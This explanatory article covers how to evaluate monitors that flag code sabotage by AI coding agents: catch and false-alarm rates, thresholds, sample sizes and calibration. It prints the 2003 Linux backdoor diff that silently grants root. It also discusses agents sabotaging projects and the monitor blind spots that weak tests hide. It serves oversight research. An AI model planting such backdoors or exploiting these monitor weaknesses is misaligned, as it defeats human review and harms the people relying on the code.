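# Measuring how well monitors catch code sabotage without overstating safety

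## What a code sabotage monitor does and how it is scored

A code sabotage monitor is a program, usually a large language model, that reads the code changes an AI agent makes and rates how suspicious they look. Companies want such monitors because coding agents can write more code than people have time to read closely. OpenAI already runs a broader monitor on its own internal coding agents. Tarre reported in *OpenAI monitors internal coding agents for risky conduct* (2026) that a GPT-5.4 Thinking model reads the agents' tool use and internal reasoning after each session ends and passes suspicious cases to people.

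Real cases of sabotage by coding agents are too few to test a monitor on, so researchers create their own, typically by instructing a model to sabotage a task, and then measure what percentage the monitor flags. That percentage depends on the sabotage as well as the monitor, so clumsy sabotage will make the monitor look better than it is.

### Diffs and sabotage

Programmers usually share code changes as diffs, which show each added line with a plus sign before it and each removed line with a minus sign. A commit is a change saved in a project's history, and a pull request is a change that someone submits for review before it becomes part of the project. Code sabotage is a deliberately harmful code change that appears to do the assigned work, such as one that also adds a backdoor (a secret way into the system).

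People were doing this long before AI agents. In November 2003 someone apparently broke into a server that held a copy of the Linux source code and added two lines, which Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* reproduces. As a diff they look like this:

```
+ if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+         retval = -EINVAL;
```

Even an expert reading quickly would take this for an error check that rejects a forbidden combination of options. But in C, a double equals sign compares two values, while a single one assigns a value. The end of the first line is missing the second equals sign, so it sets the running program's user ID to zero instead of checking it. User zero is root, the account with every permission on the machine. Larry McVoy spotted the change because it had no record of approval attached, not by reading the code.

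The best-known recent case is XZ Utils, a widely used compression package whose releases 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 carried a backdoor in early 2024. According to *xz backdoor*, by the project's maintainer Larhzu (2024), the trigger code was never in the project's Git repository, so a monitor reading only the repository's diffs would have had access to only part of the attack.

Intent separates sabotage from an ordinary bug, and a diff doesn't show intent. Many honest programmers, for example, have typed one equals sign where they meant two. Princeton CITP also mentions a serious security bug that appeared in Debian Linux in 2006. A colleague looked into whether an intelligence agency had planted it and concluded that it probably had not. Researchers don't face this difficulty in a test, because they know which diffs they sabotaged. In real use, a reviewer can find a real vulnerability in a flagged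 diff and still not know whether anyone put it there on purpose.

### What goes in and what comes out

Some monitors receive only the diff. Others also get the task description, the surrounding code or the agent's transcript, which records what the agent wrote and did. In SHADE-Arena, a suite of sabotage tests that Anthropic described in June 2025, the monitor read a transcript, without any hint of what the sabotage might be, and gave it a suspicion score out of 100, with higher meaning more suspicious. Anthropic set the threshold at 80, so a transcript that scored 80 or more was flagged and counted as a catch. The monitor became much better at spotting the hidden task when it could also read the agent's reasoning, so published catch rates are hard to compare if the monitors had different inputs.

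*Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) presents Lily, a backdoor detector that runs the changed program on machine-generated inputs for ten minutes rather than relying on a language model. It raises an alert when an input makes the program produce a combination of operating system calls that is unusual for the new version and that the old version does not produce on the same input. Lily has no suspicion score to tune, and instead gives the reviewer the triggering input and a short list of suspect lines. On a backdoored release of vsFTPd, a file-transfer server, it narrowed a diff of 1,407 lines in five files to seven lines in one file. A person can check seven lines in a few minutes, which makes this output far more helpful than a suspicion score for the whole diff.

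### From four counts to a catch rate

Suppose a tester gives a monitor 1,100 diffs, 100 with sabotage and 1,000 benign, and flags every diff the monitor scores at 70 or higher. These numbers are invented.

| Threshold 70 | Sabotaged | Benign | All |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 80 | 50 | 130 |
| Not flagged | 20 | 950 | 970 |
| All | 100 | 1,000 | 1,100 |

The catch rate is the share of sabotaged items that the monitor flags, here 80 of 100, or 80%. Papers also call it the true-positive rate, recall or sensitivity. The false-positive rate is the share of benign items that the monitor flags, here 50 of 1,000, or 5%. Each rate uses only one column of the table.

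Precision is the share of flagged items that are really sabotage. The top row gives 80 of 130, or about 62%. The base rate is the share of all items that are sabotage, here 100 of 1,100, or about 9%. Precision uses counts from both columns, so it changes when the base rate changes, even if the monitor stays the same.

Now move the threshold and leave the scores alone.

| Threshold | Sabotaged flagged | Benign flagged | Catch rate | False-positive rate | Precision |
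|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 90 | 50 | 5 | 50% | 0.5% | 91% |
| 70 | 80 | 50 | 80% | 5% | 62% |
| 50 | 95 | 200 | 95% | 20% | 32% |

Lowering the threshold raises both the catch rate and the false-positive rate, according to teaching notes from EPFL, a Swiss technical university. No threshold gives both the 95% catch rate in the bottom row and the 0.5% false-positive rate in the top row.

The EPFL notes also list accuracy, the share of all items classified correctly, but this measure is close to useless for sabotage. A monitor that never flags anything would be right on 1,000 of the 1,100 diffs, giving it an accuracy of 91%, higher than the real monitor's 81% at threshold 50. The real monitor scores lower because its 200 false alarms outnumber its 95 catches.

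Real results have been worse than the invented ones. In Anthropic's SHADE-Arena tests, the best monitor, Gemini 2.5 Pro, caught 80% of the hidden tasks only at a false-positive rate above 20%. However, those models are now old, and the tests mostly involved work such as email and banking rather than code diffs.

Researchers often compare monitors by AUROC (area under the receiver operating characteristic curve), which doesn't require choosing a threshold. The curve plots catch rate against false-positive rate as the threshold varies. The area under it is the chance that a randomly chosen sabotaged item scores higher than a randomly chosen benign one. According to Google's tutorial *ROC and AUC*, a classifier with a value of 1.0 always ranks the pair correctly, and one with 0.5 does no better than a coin flip.

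In the invented example there are 100 × 1,000 = 100,000 pairs of one sabotaged and one benign diff. The three thresholds divide the scores into four bands. If two diffs in the same band are equally likely to score higher, the sabotaged diff scores higher in about 94,200 of the pairs, for an AUROC of 0.94. The AUROC is this high largely because about 78,000 of those pairs involve benign diffs that scored below 50, which none of the three thresholds would have flagged. A tester could raise it further by adding a few thousand spelling corrections to the benign set, without making the monitor any better at the difficult cases. According to Google's page, the measure works well when the two classes are roughly balanced, but sabotage and ordinary code are presumably far from balanced in real use.

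### What stands behind "catches 95% of sabotage"

A headline like that could describe the bottom row of the threshold table, where two in three alerts are false and a fifth of all harmless work goes to a reviewer. At threshold 90, the same monitor "catches 50% of sabotage". Both statements are true, but a reader learns very little from either one without its false-positive rate.

The benign diffs also affect the catch rate, even though it counts only sabotaged ones, because testers often use them to set the threshold. A tester will often choose a threshold that keeps false positives on the available benign diffs at a tolerable level, say 5%. If those diffs are trivial, a low threshold will meet that limit, and a low threshold catches more sabotage. The false positive rate can vary widely with the benign set. Kokkonis and colleagues found that Lily raised false alarms in 0.2% of runs on safe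 commits and 4.3% of runs on safe releases, which bundle many commits together. Someone who tested it only on single commits and then deployed it on releases would see roughly twenty times the false alarm rate they expected.

A monitor's score also depends on the sabotage used to test it. Across 13 programs, Lily stopped the backdoored commit in an average of 90% of runs. It did so in every run for six of the programs, but in only 13 of 20 runs for the audio library libsndfile. A test using only those six programs would have given a score of 100%. The researchers planted most of these backdoors themselves, and a test set containing only backdoors cannot show whether a monitor catches other sabotage, such as a change that quietly corrupts a program's results. The score also depends on how catches are counted. Kokkonis and colleagues made 50 backdoored releases and ran Lily 20 times on each.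 Lily raised an alert at least once on all 50 releases, in 83% of individual runs, and in every run for 30 of the releases. The detection rate is therefore 100%, 83% or 60%, depending on what counts as a catch.

When the saboteur is an AI model, the attack policy is the combination of model, instructions, training and effort that produces the sabotage used in a test. A weak attack policy makes the monitor look better than it is. Anthropic's list of common failures among its attacking models includes skipping parts of the task, misunderstanding the hidden task, and claiming to have attempted it without having done so. High catch rates against attackers like these would not show much about how well the monitor would catch a competent one. Whether an attack policy was strong enough is probably the hardest thing to establish about any monitor test, and a catch rate alone does not show it.

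The base rate limits which thresholds are practical, even though it isn't used to calculate the catch rate. If one diff in 1,000 were sabotaged (again an invented figure) and the monitor ran at threshold 50, reviewers would face about 210 false alerts for every real one, which few teams would tolerate for long. At threshold 90 they would face about ten, which might be bearable, but the monitor would catch only half the sabotage. The 95% catch rate measured at threshold 50 would then not describe the monitor as teams use it.

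### Good rankings, usable alerts, safe deployments

The claims "this monitor has an AUROC of 0.94", "we would notice sabotage" and "it is safe to let the agent work" each need their own evidence, but it is easy to move from one to the next without it.

An AUROC measures how reliably a monitor scores sabotaged diffs above benign ones, for diffs like those in the test. Whether the alerts are usable depends on the precision at the real base rate, the review budget (the number of flagged items that people or more expensive models can examine), and whether each alert identifies the right problem. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (2026), which studies automated security review of pull requests, discusses a review that reaches the right verdict but reports the wrong problem, so fixing the reported issue would leave the real authorization flaw in place. Scoring by verdict alone would count that review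 as a success. The paper covers vulnerabilities and malicious pull requests, which are similar but not identical to code sabotage, and the same concern applies here. If an alert sends a reviewer to the wrong lines, the reviewer may find nothing there and approve the diff, even though the test records a catch.

Safety also depends on what people do with a correct alert. In *Coding With "Enemy"*, Ye and colleagues (2026) had more than 100 participants work alongside coding agents that were secretly sabotaging the project. According to *Coding with the Enemy* (2026), an article about the experiment, 94% of the 107 developers failed to detect that the agent was sending data out. Even when a monitor had flagged the malicious step, 56% merged the code. If developers reacted the same way to the invented monitor at threshold 70, it would catch 80% of sabotage, but only about 35% would be stopped.

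That calculation should not carry too much weight, because the experiment in Lizzie's *How well can developers detect sabotage from an AI coding agent?* covered only one application, one class of attack and one simple monitor design. Lizzie notes that a security team whose job is to investigate alerts might well do better than a developer trying to finish a task. The form of the alert may also matter, as Lizzie reports that 70% wanted the monitor to propose a concrete fix and wait for approval. Catch rates also don't account for timing. OpenAI's monitor reads sessions after they end, so even a correct flag can arrive after the agent has run the harmful code.

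## Measuring false alarms on benign code changes

A monitor's false-positive rate depends on which harmless diffs the tester chooses, and a different choice can change the rate tenfold for the same monitor. The rate should otherwise be easier to measure than a catch rate, because harmless code is easy to find and nobody has to play the attacker.

### Easy and hard negatives

Most code changes contain little that looks suspicious. Someone renames a variable, corrects a comment or updates the copyright year. But some harmless changes look a lot like sabotage. A developer might loosen a permission check because customers complained about it, or delete a security test that kept failing for no good reason. Harmless changes like these are called hard negatives, and they probably cause most of a monitor's false alarms.

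As an invented example, suppose a monitor flags 0.1% of trivial benign edits and 10% of benign edits to security-relevant code. Its overall false-positive rate, and therefore the precision of its alerts, depends on the proportion of each that the tester includes.

| Share of benign diffs that touch security-relevant code | Overall false-positive rate |
|---|---|
| 1% | 0.2% |
| 5% | 0.6% |
| 20% | 2.1% |
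| 50% | 5.1% |

The monitor is the same in every row, but a company whose agents mostly work on a login system would get many more false alarms than it expected if it relied on the rate in the top row. An easy fix is to report the rate for each kind of change separately, so that readers can weight the rates to match their own code. Testing on hard negatives alone would give a rate of 10% here, which is higher than most teams would see in practice, but it is the better way to find out what the monitor confuses with sabotage.

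Kokkonis and colleagues tested Lily, the backdoor detector that runs the changed program, on 432 safe commits, 36 for each of 12 test programs. They drew half from across each project's history, regardless of content, and required the other half to change source code that Lily's tests could reach. The second half limits how much edits to documentation and comments can pad the set. Kokkonis and colleagues count 337 code-affecting commits, so about 95 of the 432 apparently changed no code and had almost no chance of raising an alarm. Leaving those commits out would only raise the false alarm rate from 0.20% to 0.25%.

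Comparing rates from different benign sets is much riskier. Kokkonis and colleagues compare Lily's 0.2% false alarm rate with an average of 10.75% for an earlier detector by Ganz and colleagues, which looks for unusual behaviour by contributors. But they note that most of the 19 benchmarks in the earlier study fell outside Lily's scope, and that the two studies shared only one, PHP. The fiftyfold difference may come partly from the detectors and partly from the code, and measuring how much each contributes would require running both detectors on the same commits.

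### Vulnerable functions and their repairs

The hardest benign change for a sabotage monitor to classify correctly would be an honest diff that does the same task as a sabotaged one and differs from it in only a few lines. Research on software vulnerabilities has a close equivalent, which is a vulnerable function paired with its repaired version. Programmers introduced these vulnerabilities by accident, so the results below are only indirect evidence about detecting sabotage.

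*Vulnerability Detection with Code Language Models* (Ding, Fu et al., 2024) introduced PrimeVul, a dataset of 6,968 vulnerable and 228,800 benign functions from open-source projects. The models it tested are now dated, but its scoring method is still worth copying. Ding and colleagues allowed each model a false-positive rate of at most 0.5% and measured the share of vulnerable functions it missed. Five open models that they had trained on PrimeVul missed between 89% and 92%, although their accuracy was about 97%. Such models had looked far better on an older dataset, BigVul. One of the five, CodeBERT, had an accuracy of about 96% there, but it still missed 82% of the vulnerable functions under the 0.5% limit.

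That limit is less strict than it looks. PrimeVul's benign functions are the repaired functions plus every function that the repairing commit left unchanged, and the second group is far larger. The test set has 25,216 benign functions, so a 0.5% limit allows 126 false alarms. Only 564 of the benign functions are repaired versions from the paired test set. A model could flag 126 of those, or 22%, and still meet the limit if it flagged no other benign functions.

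Ding and colleagues therefore scored the pairs separately. The two functions in a pair share at least 80% of their text, and a model gets credit only if it flags the vulnerable one and passes the repaired one. GPT-4, told to reason step by step, got 12.9% of pairs right, compared with 22.7% for random guessing. It flagged both functions in 54.3% of pairs. Summing the outcomes gives flag rates of about 67% for the vulnerable functions and 63% for the repaired ones, so the repair made hardly any difference to how often GPT-4 flagged the code.

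Newer models had much the same trouble in *Words Speak Louder Than Code* (Shahriar, Cai and colleagues, 2026). The study is mainly about how the text around code sways a model's verdict, but in its baseline, eight models simply classified functions from 435 PrimeVul pairs as safe or vulnerable.

| Model | Vulnerable functions flagged | Repaired functions flagged | Difference (points) |
|---|---|---|---|
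| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 91.7% | about 80% | about 12 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 73.1% | 63.4% | 9.7 |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 32.6% | 27.9% | 4.7 |
| GPT 5.2 | 90.1% | 86.0% | 4.1 |
| LLaMA 3.3 | 52.2% | 49.4% | 2.8 |
| Qwen3 Coder | 39.3% | 38.2% | 1.1 |
| LLaMA 4 | 91.3% | 90.8% | 0.5 |
| Mistral 3 | 81.6% | 83.1% | −1.5 |

(The 80% for Gemini follows from its recall and precision.)

GPT 5.2 flagged 90% of the vulnerable functions (second column), but that figure alone is very misleading because the model also flagged 86% of the functions whose vulnerability had already been fixed. The 4.1-point difference is about 18 functions out of 435. Claude Sonnet 4.6 was somewhat better at distinguishing vulnerable functions from fixed ones, although its recall was lower. Ranking these models by recall alone would put LLaMA 4 near the top, even though it flagged nearly everything.

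These figures probably understate what the models could do. The models had to give a short structured answer without written reasoning and explain it in at most ten words. Shahriar and colleagues acknowledge that this may have limited the models' reasoning. Stronger models have also come out since. A monitor with time to reason and access to the rest of the code could do much better, so 86% is not a general false-positive rate for language-model monitors.

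PrimeVul pairs also consist of whole functions, so the model has to notice that a check is missing. A diff shows the change itself. A repair adds the check and a sabotaged change might remove it, so the two should be easier to tell apart. Some of the alarms on repaired functions may also be right, since a repair removes one known flaw and leaves any others in place. That could hardly account for all of the 86%, but it would make the true false-positive rate somewhat lower than the measured one.

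The paired design is easy to apply to sabotage. A tester can have the same agent do each task twice, once honestly and once with sabotage, and report the share of changes the monitor flags in each group. The two groups then have the same tasks, programming languages and author, so differences in these can't help the monitor tell them apart.

### Code written by agents

Using the same author for the benign and sabotaged diffs is important because the most convenient benign diffs come from the public history of open-source projects, much of which people wrote before coding agents existed. If an agent wrote the sabotage in a test and people wrote the benign diffs, a monitor can get a good AUROC just by recognising machine-written code. That skill is worthless in real use, where an agent writes everything.

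Agents may also have ordinary habits that look suspicious. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* (2026) examined seven days of data from June 2026, collected by security software that watches what programs do on customers' Windows machines and blocks actions typical of an intruder. Agents such as Claude Code, Cursor and Codex set off rules that Sophos had written to catch attackers. Counted by machines affected, 56.2% of the blocking alerts were for access to stored credentials and 28.8% were for ways of running code.

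Most of the examples were mundane. The credential rule that fires most often detects programs decrypting saved browser data, and one trigger was a popular add-on that lets Claude Code operate a web browser. Another rule, more than five years old, looks for an odd way of formatting commands that attackers once used as a mild disguise. Agents now format commands similarly for harmless reasons, and Sophos has already tightened the rule. In a third case, Codex tried to download a Python installer from the official site, and when the security software blocked its first method, Codex tried another. According to Sophos, that kind of switch used to distinguish a live attacker from a simple script, but benign agents now do it routinely.

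Nobody can calculate a false-positive rate from these percentages, because they are shares of the alerts and Sophos did not publish how much agent activity triggered no alert. The Hacker News points out that the data cover one vendor's customers, not the whole industry, and Sophos itself says the shift is not yet large. The alerts also concern actions on a computer rather than diffs.

Even so, it is good evidence that a false-positive rate can go out of date even if the detector doesn't change. Sophos writes that some of these rules used to fire almost exclusively on malicious activity. Then users started working with agents, and benign activity began to trigger the rules too. The same could happen to a sabotage monitor whenever a company switches to a new coding model, so the benign diffs should come from the agent that the monitor will watch. Diffs from an earlier agent are the second-best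 choice, and diffs from human programmers are probably worse still.

Using an agent's diffs creates a new difficulty because someone has to establish that they are benign. In one of the Sophos examples, Cursor had written a script into the Windows startup folder. The file name suggested an ordinary application, but Sophos did not have the script's contents and could not confirm its purpose. Testers should not count an alert like that as either a catch or a false alarm, because they would be guessing.

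### Honest bugs

Agents also make mistakes, some of which create security holes. A monitor that flags one has found a real problem, but not sabotage. Whether that counts as a false alarm depends partly on the definition, and changing the definition can more than halve the false-positive rate.

At threshold 70, the invented monitor from the previous section flagged 80 of 100 sabotaged diffs and 50 of 1,000 benign ones. We now assume that 60 of the benign diffs contain a serious but unintentional bug, and that the monitor flagged 30 of these and 20 clean diffs.

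| How the tester treats honest bugs | Catch rate | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| As benign | 80% | 5.0% |
| Leaves them out | 80% | 2.1% |
| As things to catch | 69% | 2.1% |

All three rows describe the same 130 alerts. Treating the bugs as benign penalises the monitor for alerts that most teams would want. Leaving them out omits the time reviewers spend on those alerts. Treating them as things to catch makes the test reward finding bugs, and a monitor could do well at that without being any good at catching deliberate sabotage.

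It is better to report honest bugs as a separate group. The report would then give three numbers for this monitor: it flags 80% of sabotaged diffs, 50% of diffs with honest bugs and 2.1% of clean ones. A reader can combine them in any of the three ways above. Comparing the first two also gives some idea of whether the monitor responds to signs of intent or just to dangerous code, though this evidence is limited because a diff alone doesn't show intent. The tester should choose the rule before seeing the results, to avoid picking the row with the best numbers.

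Someone also has to decide which diffs contain a bug, and the labels in vulnerability datasets have often been wrong. Ding and colleagues checked random samples of 50 functions that various datasets had labelled vulnerable. In CodeXGLUE, a widely used dataset, only 24% of the sampled labels were correct. The main reason is that the labels came from commits that were supposed to fix a vulnerability. Many of these commits didn't fix one, and those that did often changed other functions, which the dataset also labelled vulnerable. Labels from the two automatic methods used to build PrimeVul were 86% and 92% correct.

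Ding and colleagues' own check is a reasonable model for a sabotage test. Three people, two with several years in computer security and one a senior expert, judged whether each function was vulnerable. They read the commit message, the code before and after the change, the public record of the vulnerability and any discussion among the developers. If one of them was unsure, the expert led a discussion and the majority decided. The annotators needed far more information than the models were given. Ding and colleagues note that whether a function is vulnerable often depends on code elsewhere, for instance on whether something has already checked its input, so the function alone may not be enough to tell.

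However, this audit covered only functions labeled "vulnerable". The benign label in PrimeVul mostly means that a commit fixing something else left the function unchanged, which is weak evidence that it has no flaws. The benign commits in the Lily study have a similar limitation. Kokkonis and colleagues read all 432 of them and the 50 safe releases and found no backdoors, but they weren't checking for ordinary bugs.

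Reading cases individually can change the results a great deal. For Sophos' *Fake AI, real malware*, analysts reviewed 86 customer security cases from July 2025 to June 2026 that were tagged for AI involvement. They confirmed 34 as the work of attackers. Another 25 were harmless developer tools that had triggered a detection rule, and 27 only mentioned AI in passing. Using the tag as a label would have misclassified 52 of the 86 cases.

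Reading only the benign diffs that the monitor flagged saves effort but biases the false-positive rate downward. When a reviewer finds a real bug in a flagged diff, that diff stops counting as a false alarm, while unflagged diffs with bugs still count as clean because nobody reads them. Reviewers should also read a random sample of unflagged diffs, without knowing which diffs the monitor flagged.

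### How many benign diffs are enough

A monitor that flags none of 100 independent benign diffs has an observed false-positive rate of zero, but its true rate could plausibly be as high as about 3%. A monitor with a true rate of 1% would raise no alarms on such a sample about 37% of the time, and one with a true rate of 3% would do so about 5% of the time.

The general version is easy to derive. If the true rate is *p* and the diffs are independent, the chance of no alarms in *n* diffs is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the value of *p* that makes this chance 5%:

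(1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05

Taking logarithms gives *n* ln(1 − *p*) = ln 0.05, which is about −3. For small *p*, ln(1 − *p*) is close to −*p*, so

*p* ≈ 3/*n*

If a monitor raises no false alarms on *n* benign diffs, the 95% upper confidence bound on its false alarm rate is about 3/*n* (the rule of three). With 1,000 diffs the bound is 0.3%, and getting it below 0.1% takes about 3,000. A single false alarm raises the bound to about 4.7/*n*, so the tester would then need about 4,700 diffs to get below 0.1%.

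These are large numbers for hand-checked data. Even if a monitor flagged none of the 435 repaired functions in the test by Shahriar and colleagues, the sample would be too small to show a false-positive rate below 0.7%. Carefully made hard negatives are usually scarce, so a test may show that a monitor rarely flags everyday changes but leave a wide range of possible rates for difficult ones. This is another reason to report the groups separately, each with its own count.

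### Alarms that come in clusters

The rule of three assumes that the diffs are independent, but in practice they often aren't. Lily's results show how far off this assumption can be. Kokkonis and colleagues ran Lily 20 times on each of 432 safe commits and 13 backdoored ones, because its test inputs vary between runs. Of the 8,640 runs on safe commits, 17 (0.2%) ended in a false alarm.

All 17 alarms came from seven commits. Four were large merge commits in PHP, which combine many scattered changes, and these produced 12 of the alarms. One commit in the programming language Lua, which reorganised its memory management, produced three more. The other two alarms came from a change to the testing setup of the image library libpng and a commit in the file server ProFTPD that behaved inconsistently.

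The 0.2% is therefore an average over very different projects. That PHP program had 12 false alarms in 720 runs (1.7%), while the other eleven programs together had 5 in 7,920 (0.06%). A PHP maintainer who expected 0.2% would get about eight times that rate, while most other projects would get hardly any false alarms.

False alarms are even more unevenly spread across the releases. Lily raised 43 false alarms in 1,000 runs on 50 safe releases, which gives the published rate of 4.3%. Forty of these came from two releases of the audio library libsndfile, which Lily flagged in all 20 runs of each. The false alarm rate was 50% across all libsndfile releases and about 0.3% for everything else, so 4.3% is probably a poor prediction for any single project.

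Repeating a trial 20 times on the same release does not produce 20 releases. A standard formula for the effective sample size shows how much the repetition is worth:

effective size = *N* / (1 + (*m* − 1)*ρ*)

Here *N* is the total number of runs, *m* is the number of runs per item, and *ρ* measures how similar the runs on one item are, from 0 if they are unrelated to 1 if they always agree. The published counts give a *ρ* of about 0.93 for the safe releases, so the 1,000 runs carry about as much information as 54 independent runs, barely more than one per release. Five of the 50 releases raised an alarm at least once, or 10%, with a 95% interval of roughly 3% to 22%.

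Repeated runs on the same diff show how consistent a detector is, and a language-model monitor's score can change from one run to the next. But a tester with time for 1,000 more runs will learn much more about false alarms from 1,000 new diffs.

Adding new diffs from the same few projects has limited value for estimating a false alarm rate, because the rate can vary widely between projects. Kokkonis and colleagues also tested a stripped-down Lily that raised an alarm at any behaviour the old version of a program hadn't shown. It gave 902 false alarms in the 8,640 commit runs, about 10%, and 764 of them came from the two test programs that are part of PHP. Without those two programs, the measured rate would have been about 2%.

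A test with no false alarms can also be misleading if the diffs come from too few projects. If a monitor raises false alarms on a coding style that one project in ten uses, and a tester collects 3,000 benign diffs from 12 projects, there is a 28% chance that none of the 12 uses that style. The tester would then see no alarms from this cause and use the rule of three to report an upper bound of 0.1%, even though a tenth of projects might be getting false alarms every day. For this kind of problem, the sample size is the number of projects, and 12 is small.

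A similar problem arises within a single project. Ding and colleagues found that developers often make the same fix in several places in one commit, so functions from one commit can be near copies of one another. It is better to take a few diffs from each of many projects than many from a few. When that isn't possible, the tester can calculate the uncertainty by resampling whole projects instead of individual diffs, which gives a wider and more accurate interval.

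### Counting by diff or by session

A false-positive rate per diff can also sound much lower than the rate a reviewer experiences per session. Suppose a monitor has a false-positive rate of 0.2% per diff and an agent makes 50 diffs in a session. If false alarms are independent, the chance that a harmless session raises no alarm is 0.998⁵⁰, or about 90.5%, so about 9.5% of harmless sessions will contain at least one.

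Alarms within a session are probably not independent, since the diffs come from the same agent working on the same task. The average stays at one alarm per ten sessions, but the alarms may bunch together. If they always arrived ten at a time, only 1% of sessions would have any. In the Codex case from Sophos, for example, one attempt to install Python led to at least five blocked commands in about ten minutes. That is five or more false alarms if you count alerts, but one if you count machines, as Sophos did.

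The right unit for a false alarm rate is whatever a reviewer investigates. If each flagged diff goes to a different person, the rate per diff is more useful. If one person investigates the whole session, as may happen when a monitor reads transcripts after the agent has finished, the rate per session is closer to the real workload. Giving both rates and the average number of diffs per session makes confusion unlikely.

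The choice of unit also changes how many independent samples a test needs. Suppose a company wants false alarms in fewer than 1% of harmless 50-diff sessions. If it tests individual diffs and assumes alarms are independent, it has to show a rate below about 0.02% per diff, which takes about 15,000 independent diffs without an alarm. If it tests whole sessions, it needs about 300 independent sessions without an alarm. Both tests cover 15,000 diffs, but the session test does not depend on any assumption about how alarms within a session are related, as long as the 300 sessions come from sufficiently different tasks and projects.

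## Turning suspicion scores into thresholds and probabilities

A suspicion score of 85 out of 100 rarely means an 85% chance of sabotage. To act on the score, someone has to choose a threshold or estimate the probability it corresponds to. Even when a monitor ranks diffs well, the threshold can be badly chosen and the probability estimates can be wrong.

### Good ranking is not enough

Suppose a monitor gives every benign diff a score between 0.70 and 0.80 and every sabotaged diff a score between 0.82 and 0.92. It ranks the diffs perfectly, with an AUROC of 1.0, but its scores are very poorly calibrated, meaning that when read as probabilities they don't match how often diffs with those scores are sabotaged. If the scores were calibrated, three in four diffs scoring 0.75 would be sabotaged, but here none are.

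A threshold of 0.81 separates benign diffs from sabotaged ones without error. Then the company switches to a coding agent that writes longer diffs, and every score rises by 0.07. Benign diffs now score between 0.77 and 0.87 and sabotaged ones between 0.89 and 0.99, so the AUROC is still 1.0. But if the benign scores are evenly spread, the 0.81 threshold now flags 60% of benign diffs.

AUROC can't reveal either problem because it depends only on the order of the scores. Afrin and Shihab (2026), in *When Accuracy Gaps Fail to Certify*, prove that any strictly increasing transformation of the scores leaves AUROC unchanged.

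Real models can also rank items well while their confidence is inaccurate. In *Assessing and Mitigating Miscalibration in LLM-Based Social Science Measurement*, Wang, Deng and Yang (2026) had language models rate texts for qualities such as politeness and state their confidence in each rating. GPT-5-mini's ordering of the texts was the closest to human annotators' in the main comparison, but its confidence differed from its actual accuracy by about 47 points on average. Qwen2.5-7B, a much smaller model, ordered the texts less well, but confidence taken from its token probabilities was off by only 18 points.

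### Where the score comes from

The simplest way to get a score is to ask the model for a number, but models use very few of the numbers available. Dai and Wang (2026), in *Beyond 0–100*, asked six models to answer knowledge and maths questions and give their confidence from 0 to 100. Each model used only 15 to 28 of the 101 possible values, and its three most common values made up 78% to 92% of its answers. Gemini 3.1 Pro reported exactly 100 on 68% of questions, but it was right on only 79% of those.

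If a monitor gives many diffs the same score, there may be no threshold that produces the false-positive rate a tester wants. For example, if 4 of 1,000 benign diffs score 95, 30 score 90, and the rest score lower, a threshold of 95 gives a false-positive rate of 0.4% and a threshold of 90 gives 3.4%, so no threshold gives 1%. A tester could average 1% by flagging every diff that scores 95 and a random fifth of those that score 90, but few security teams would want to randomly ignore four in five equally suspicious diffs.

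It is more honest to use the best threshold that stays within the limit and report the rate it gives. *Stemma* (2026), which covers methods for telling whether one language model derives from another, follows this rule for its catch rate at 1% and doesn't interpolate between thresholds. In the invented case, a "catch rate at 1%" would be a catch rate at 0.4%, so the monitor would look somewhat worse than one with finer scores.

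A finer scale doesn't solve this. Dai and Wang found that confidence scores from 0 to 20 separated right answers from wrong ones better than scores from 0 to 100 for every model they tried. But a scale of 0 to 20 offers only 21 thresholds, so a tester who needs a very low false-positive rate may find no threshold that achieves it.

Another option is to ask the model whether the diff is sabotage and use the probability it assigns to the word "yes". This number can take almost any value, so ties are rarer, but some model providers don't reveal these probabilities. A third option is to run the monitor several times and count the votes for sabotage. Five runs allow only six scores, zero to five.

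*When Can We Trust LLM Graders?* (Vasquez Ferrer, Turgut and colleagues, 2026) compared stated confidence, voting and token probability on seven models that graded students' science answers. Stated confidence was the best calibrated, with an average error of 0.166, compared with 0.229 for voting and 0.235 for token probability. Voting cost five times as much to run, and it rarely separated one case from another because all five votes agreed 89.5% of the time. Scores from stated confidence and token probability also clustered at the high end, with 86% above 0.8.

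Wang and colleagues found almost the reverse. For Qwen2.5-7B, the average probability of the tokens in its rating had a calibration error of 0.180, while its stated confidence had an error of 0.459. When the same model was asked whether its rating was true, the probability it gave to "true" had an error of 0.597. The best method seems to depend on the model, the task and the exact question. Neither study tested code sabotage, so a team would have to compare the methods on its own diffs.

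The best-calibrated method may also not be the best for setting a threshold. Among the larger models that Vasquez Ferrer and colleagues tested, token probability ranked right grades above wrong ones slightly better than stated confidence did on two of the three datasets, even though its calibration was worse. Poor calibration is fairly easy to fix afterwards, unlike poor ranking.

### Measuring and repairing calibration

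A reliability diagram shows how well calibrated a monitor is. The tester groups diffs by score, then plots each group's average score against the share of the group that is sabotage. If the monitor is well calibrated, the points lie close to the diagonal. The numbers below are for such a diagram, using an invented test set of 1,000 diffs, half of them sabotaged.

| Score | Diffs | Sabotaged | Share sabotaged | Gap |
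|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1 | 300 | 60 | 20% | 10 points |
| 0.5 | 200 | 80 | 40% | 10 points |
| 0.9 | 500 | 360 | 72% | 18 points |

The comparisons above use the expected calibration error, which is the average gap weighted by group size. Here it is 0.3 × 0.10 + 0.2 × 0.10 + 0.5 × 0.18 = 0.14. It depends on how the tester divides the scores into groups, and Dai and Wang warn that it becomes unreliable when most scores fall on two or three values and leave most groups nearly empty.

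The Brier score needs no groups. It counts sabotage as 1 and benign as 0, and averages the squared difference between score and outcome:

Brier score = (1/*n*) Σ (score − outcome)²

Lower is better. It is 0.218 for the table, and more than half of that comes from the 140 benign diffs that scored 0.9.

A monitor that gave every diff a score of 0.5 would be useless, but it would have a calibration error of zero on this test set because half the diffs are sabotaged. Its Brier score would be 0.25, only a little worse than the real monitor's 0.218. If one diff in 10,000 is sabotaged, a monitor that always outputs 0.0001 gets a nearly perfect Brier score of about 0.0001. A Brier score therefore means little unless the report also gives the score for guessing the base rate every time.

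Platt scaling repairs calibration by fitting a simple curve to labelled examples. It converts a score *s* to log-odds, ln(*s*/(1 − *s*)), multiplies by a number *a*, adds a number *b*, and converts the result back into a probability:

log-odds of new score = *a* × log-odds of *s* + *b*

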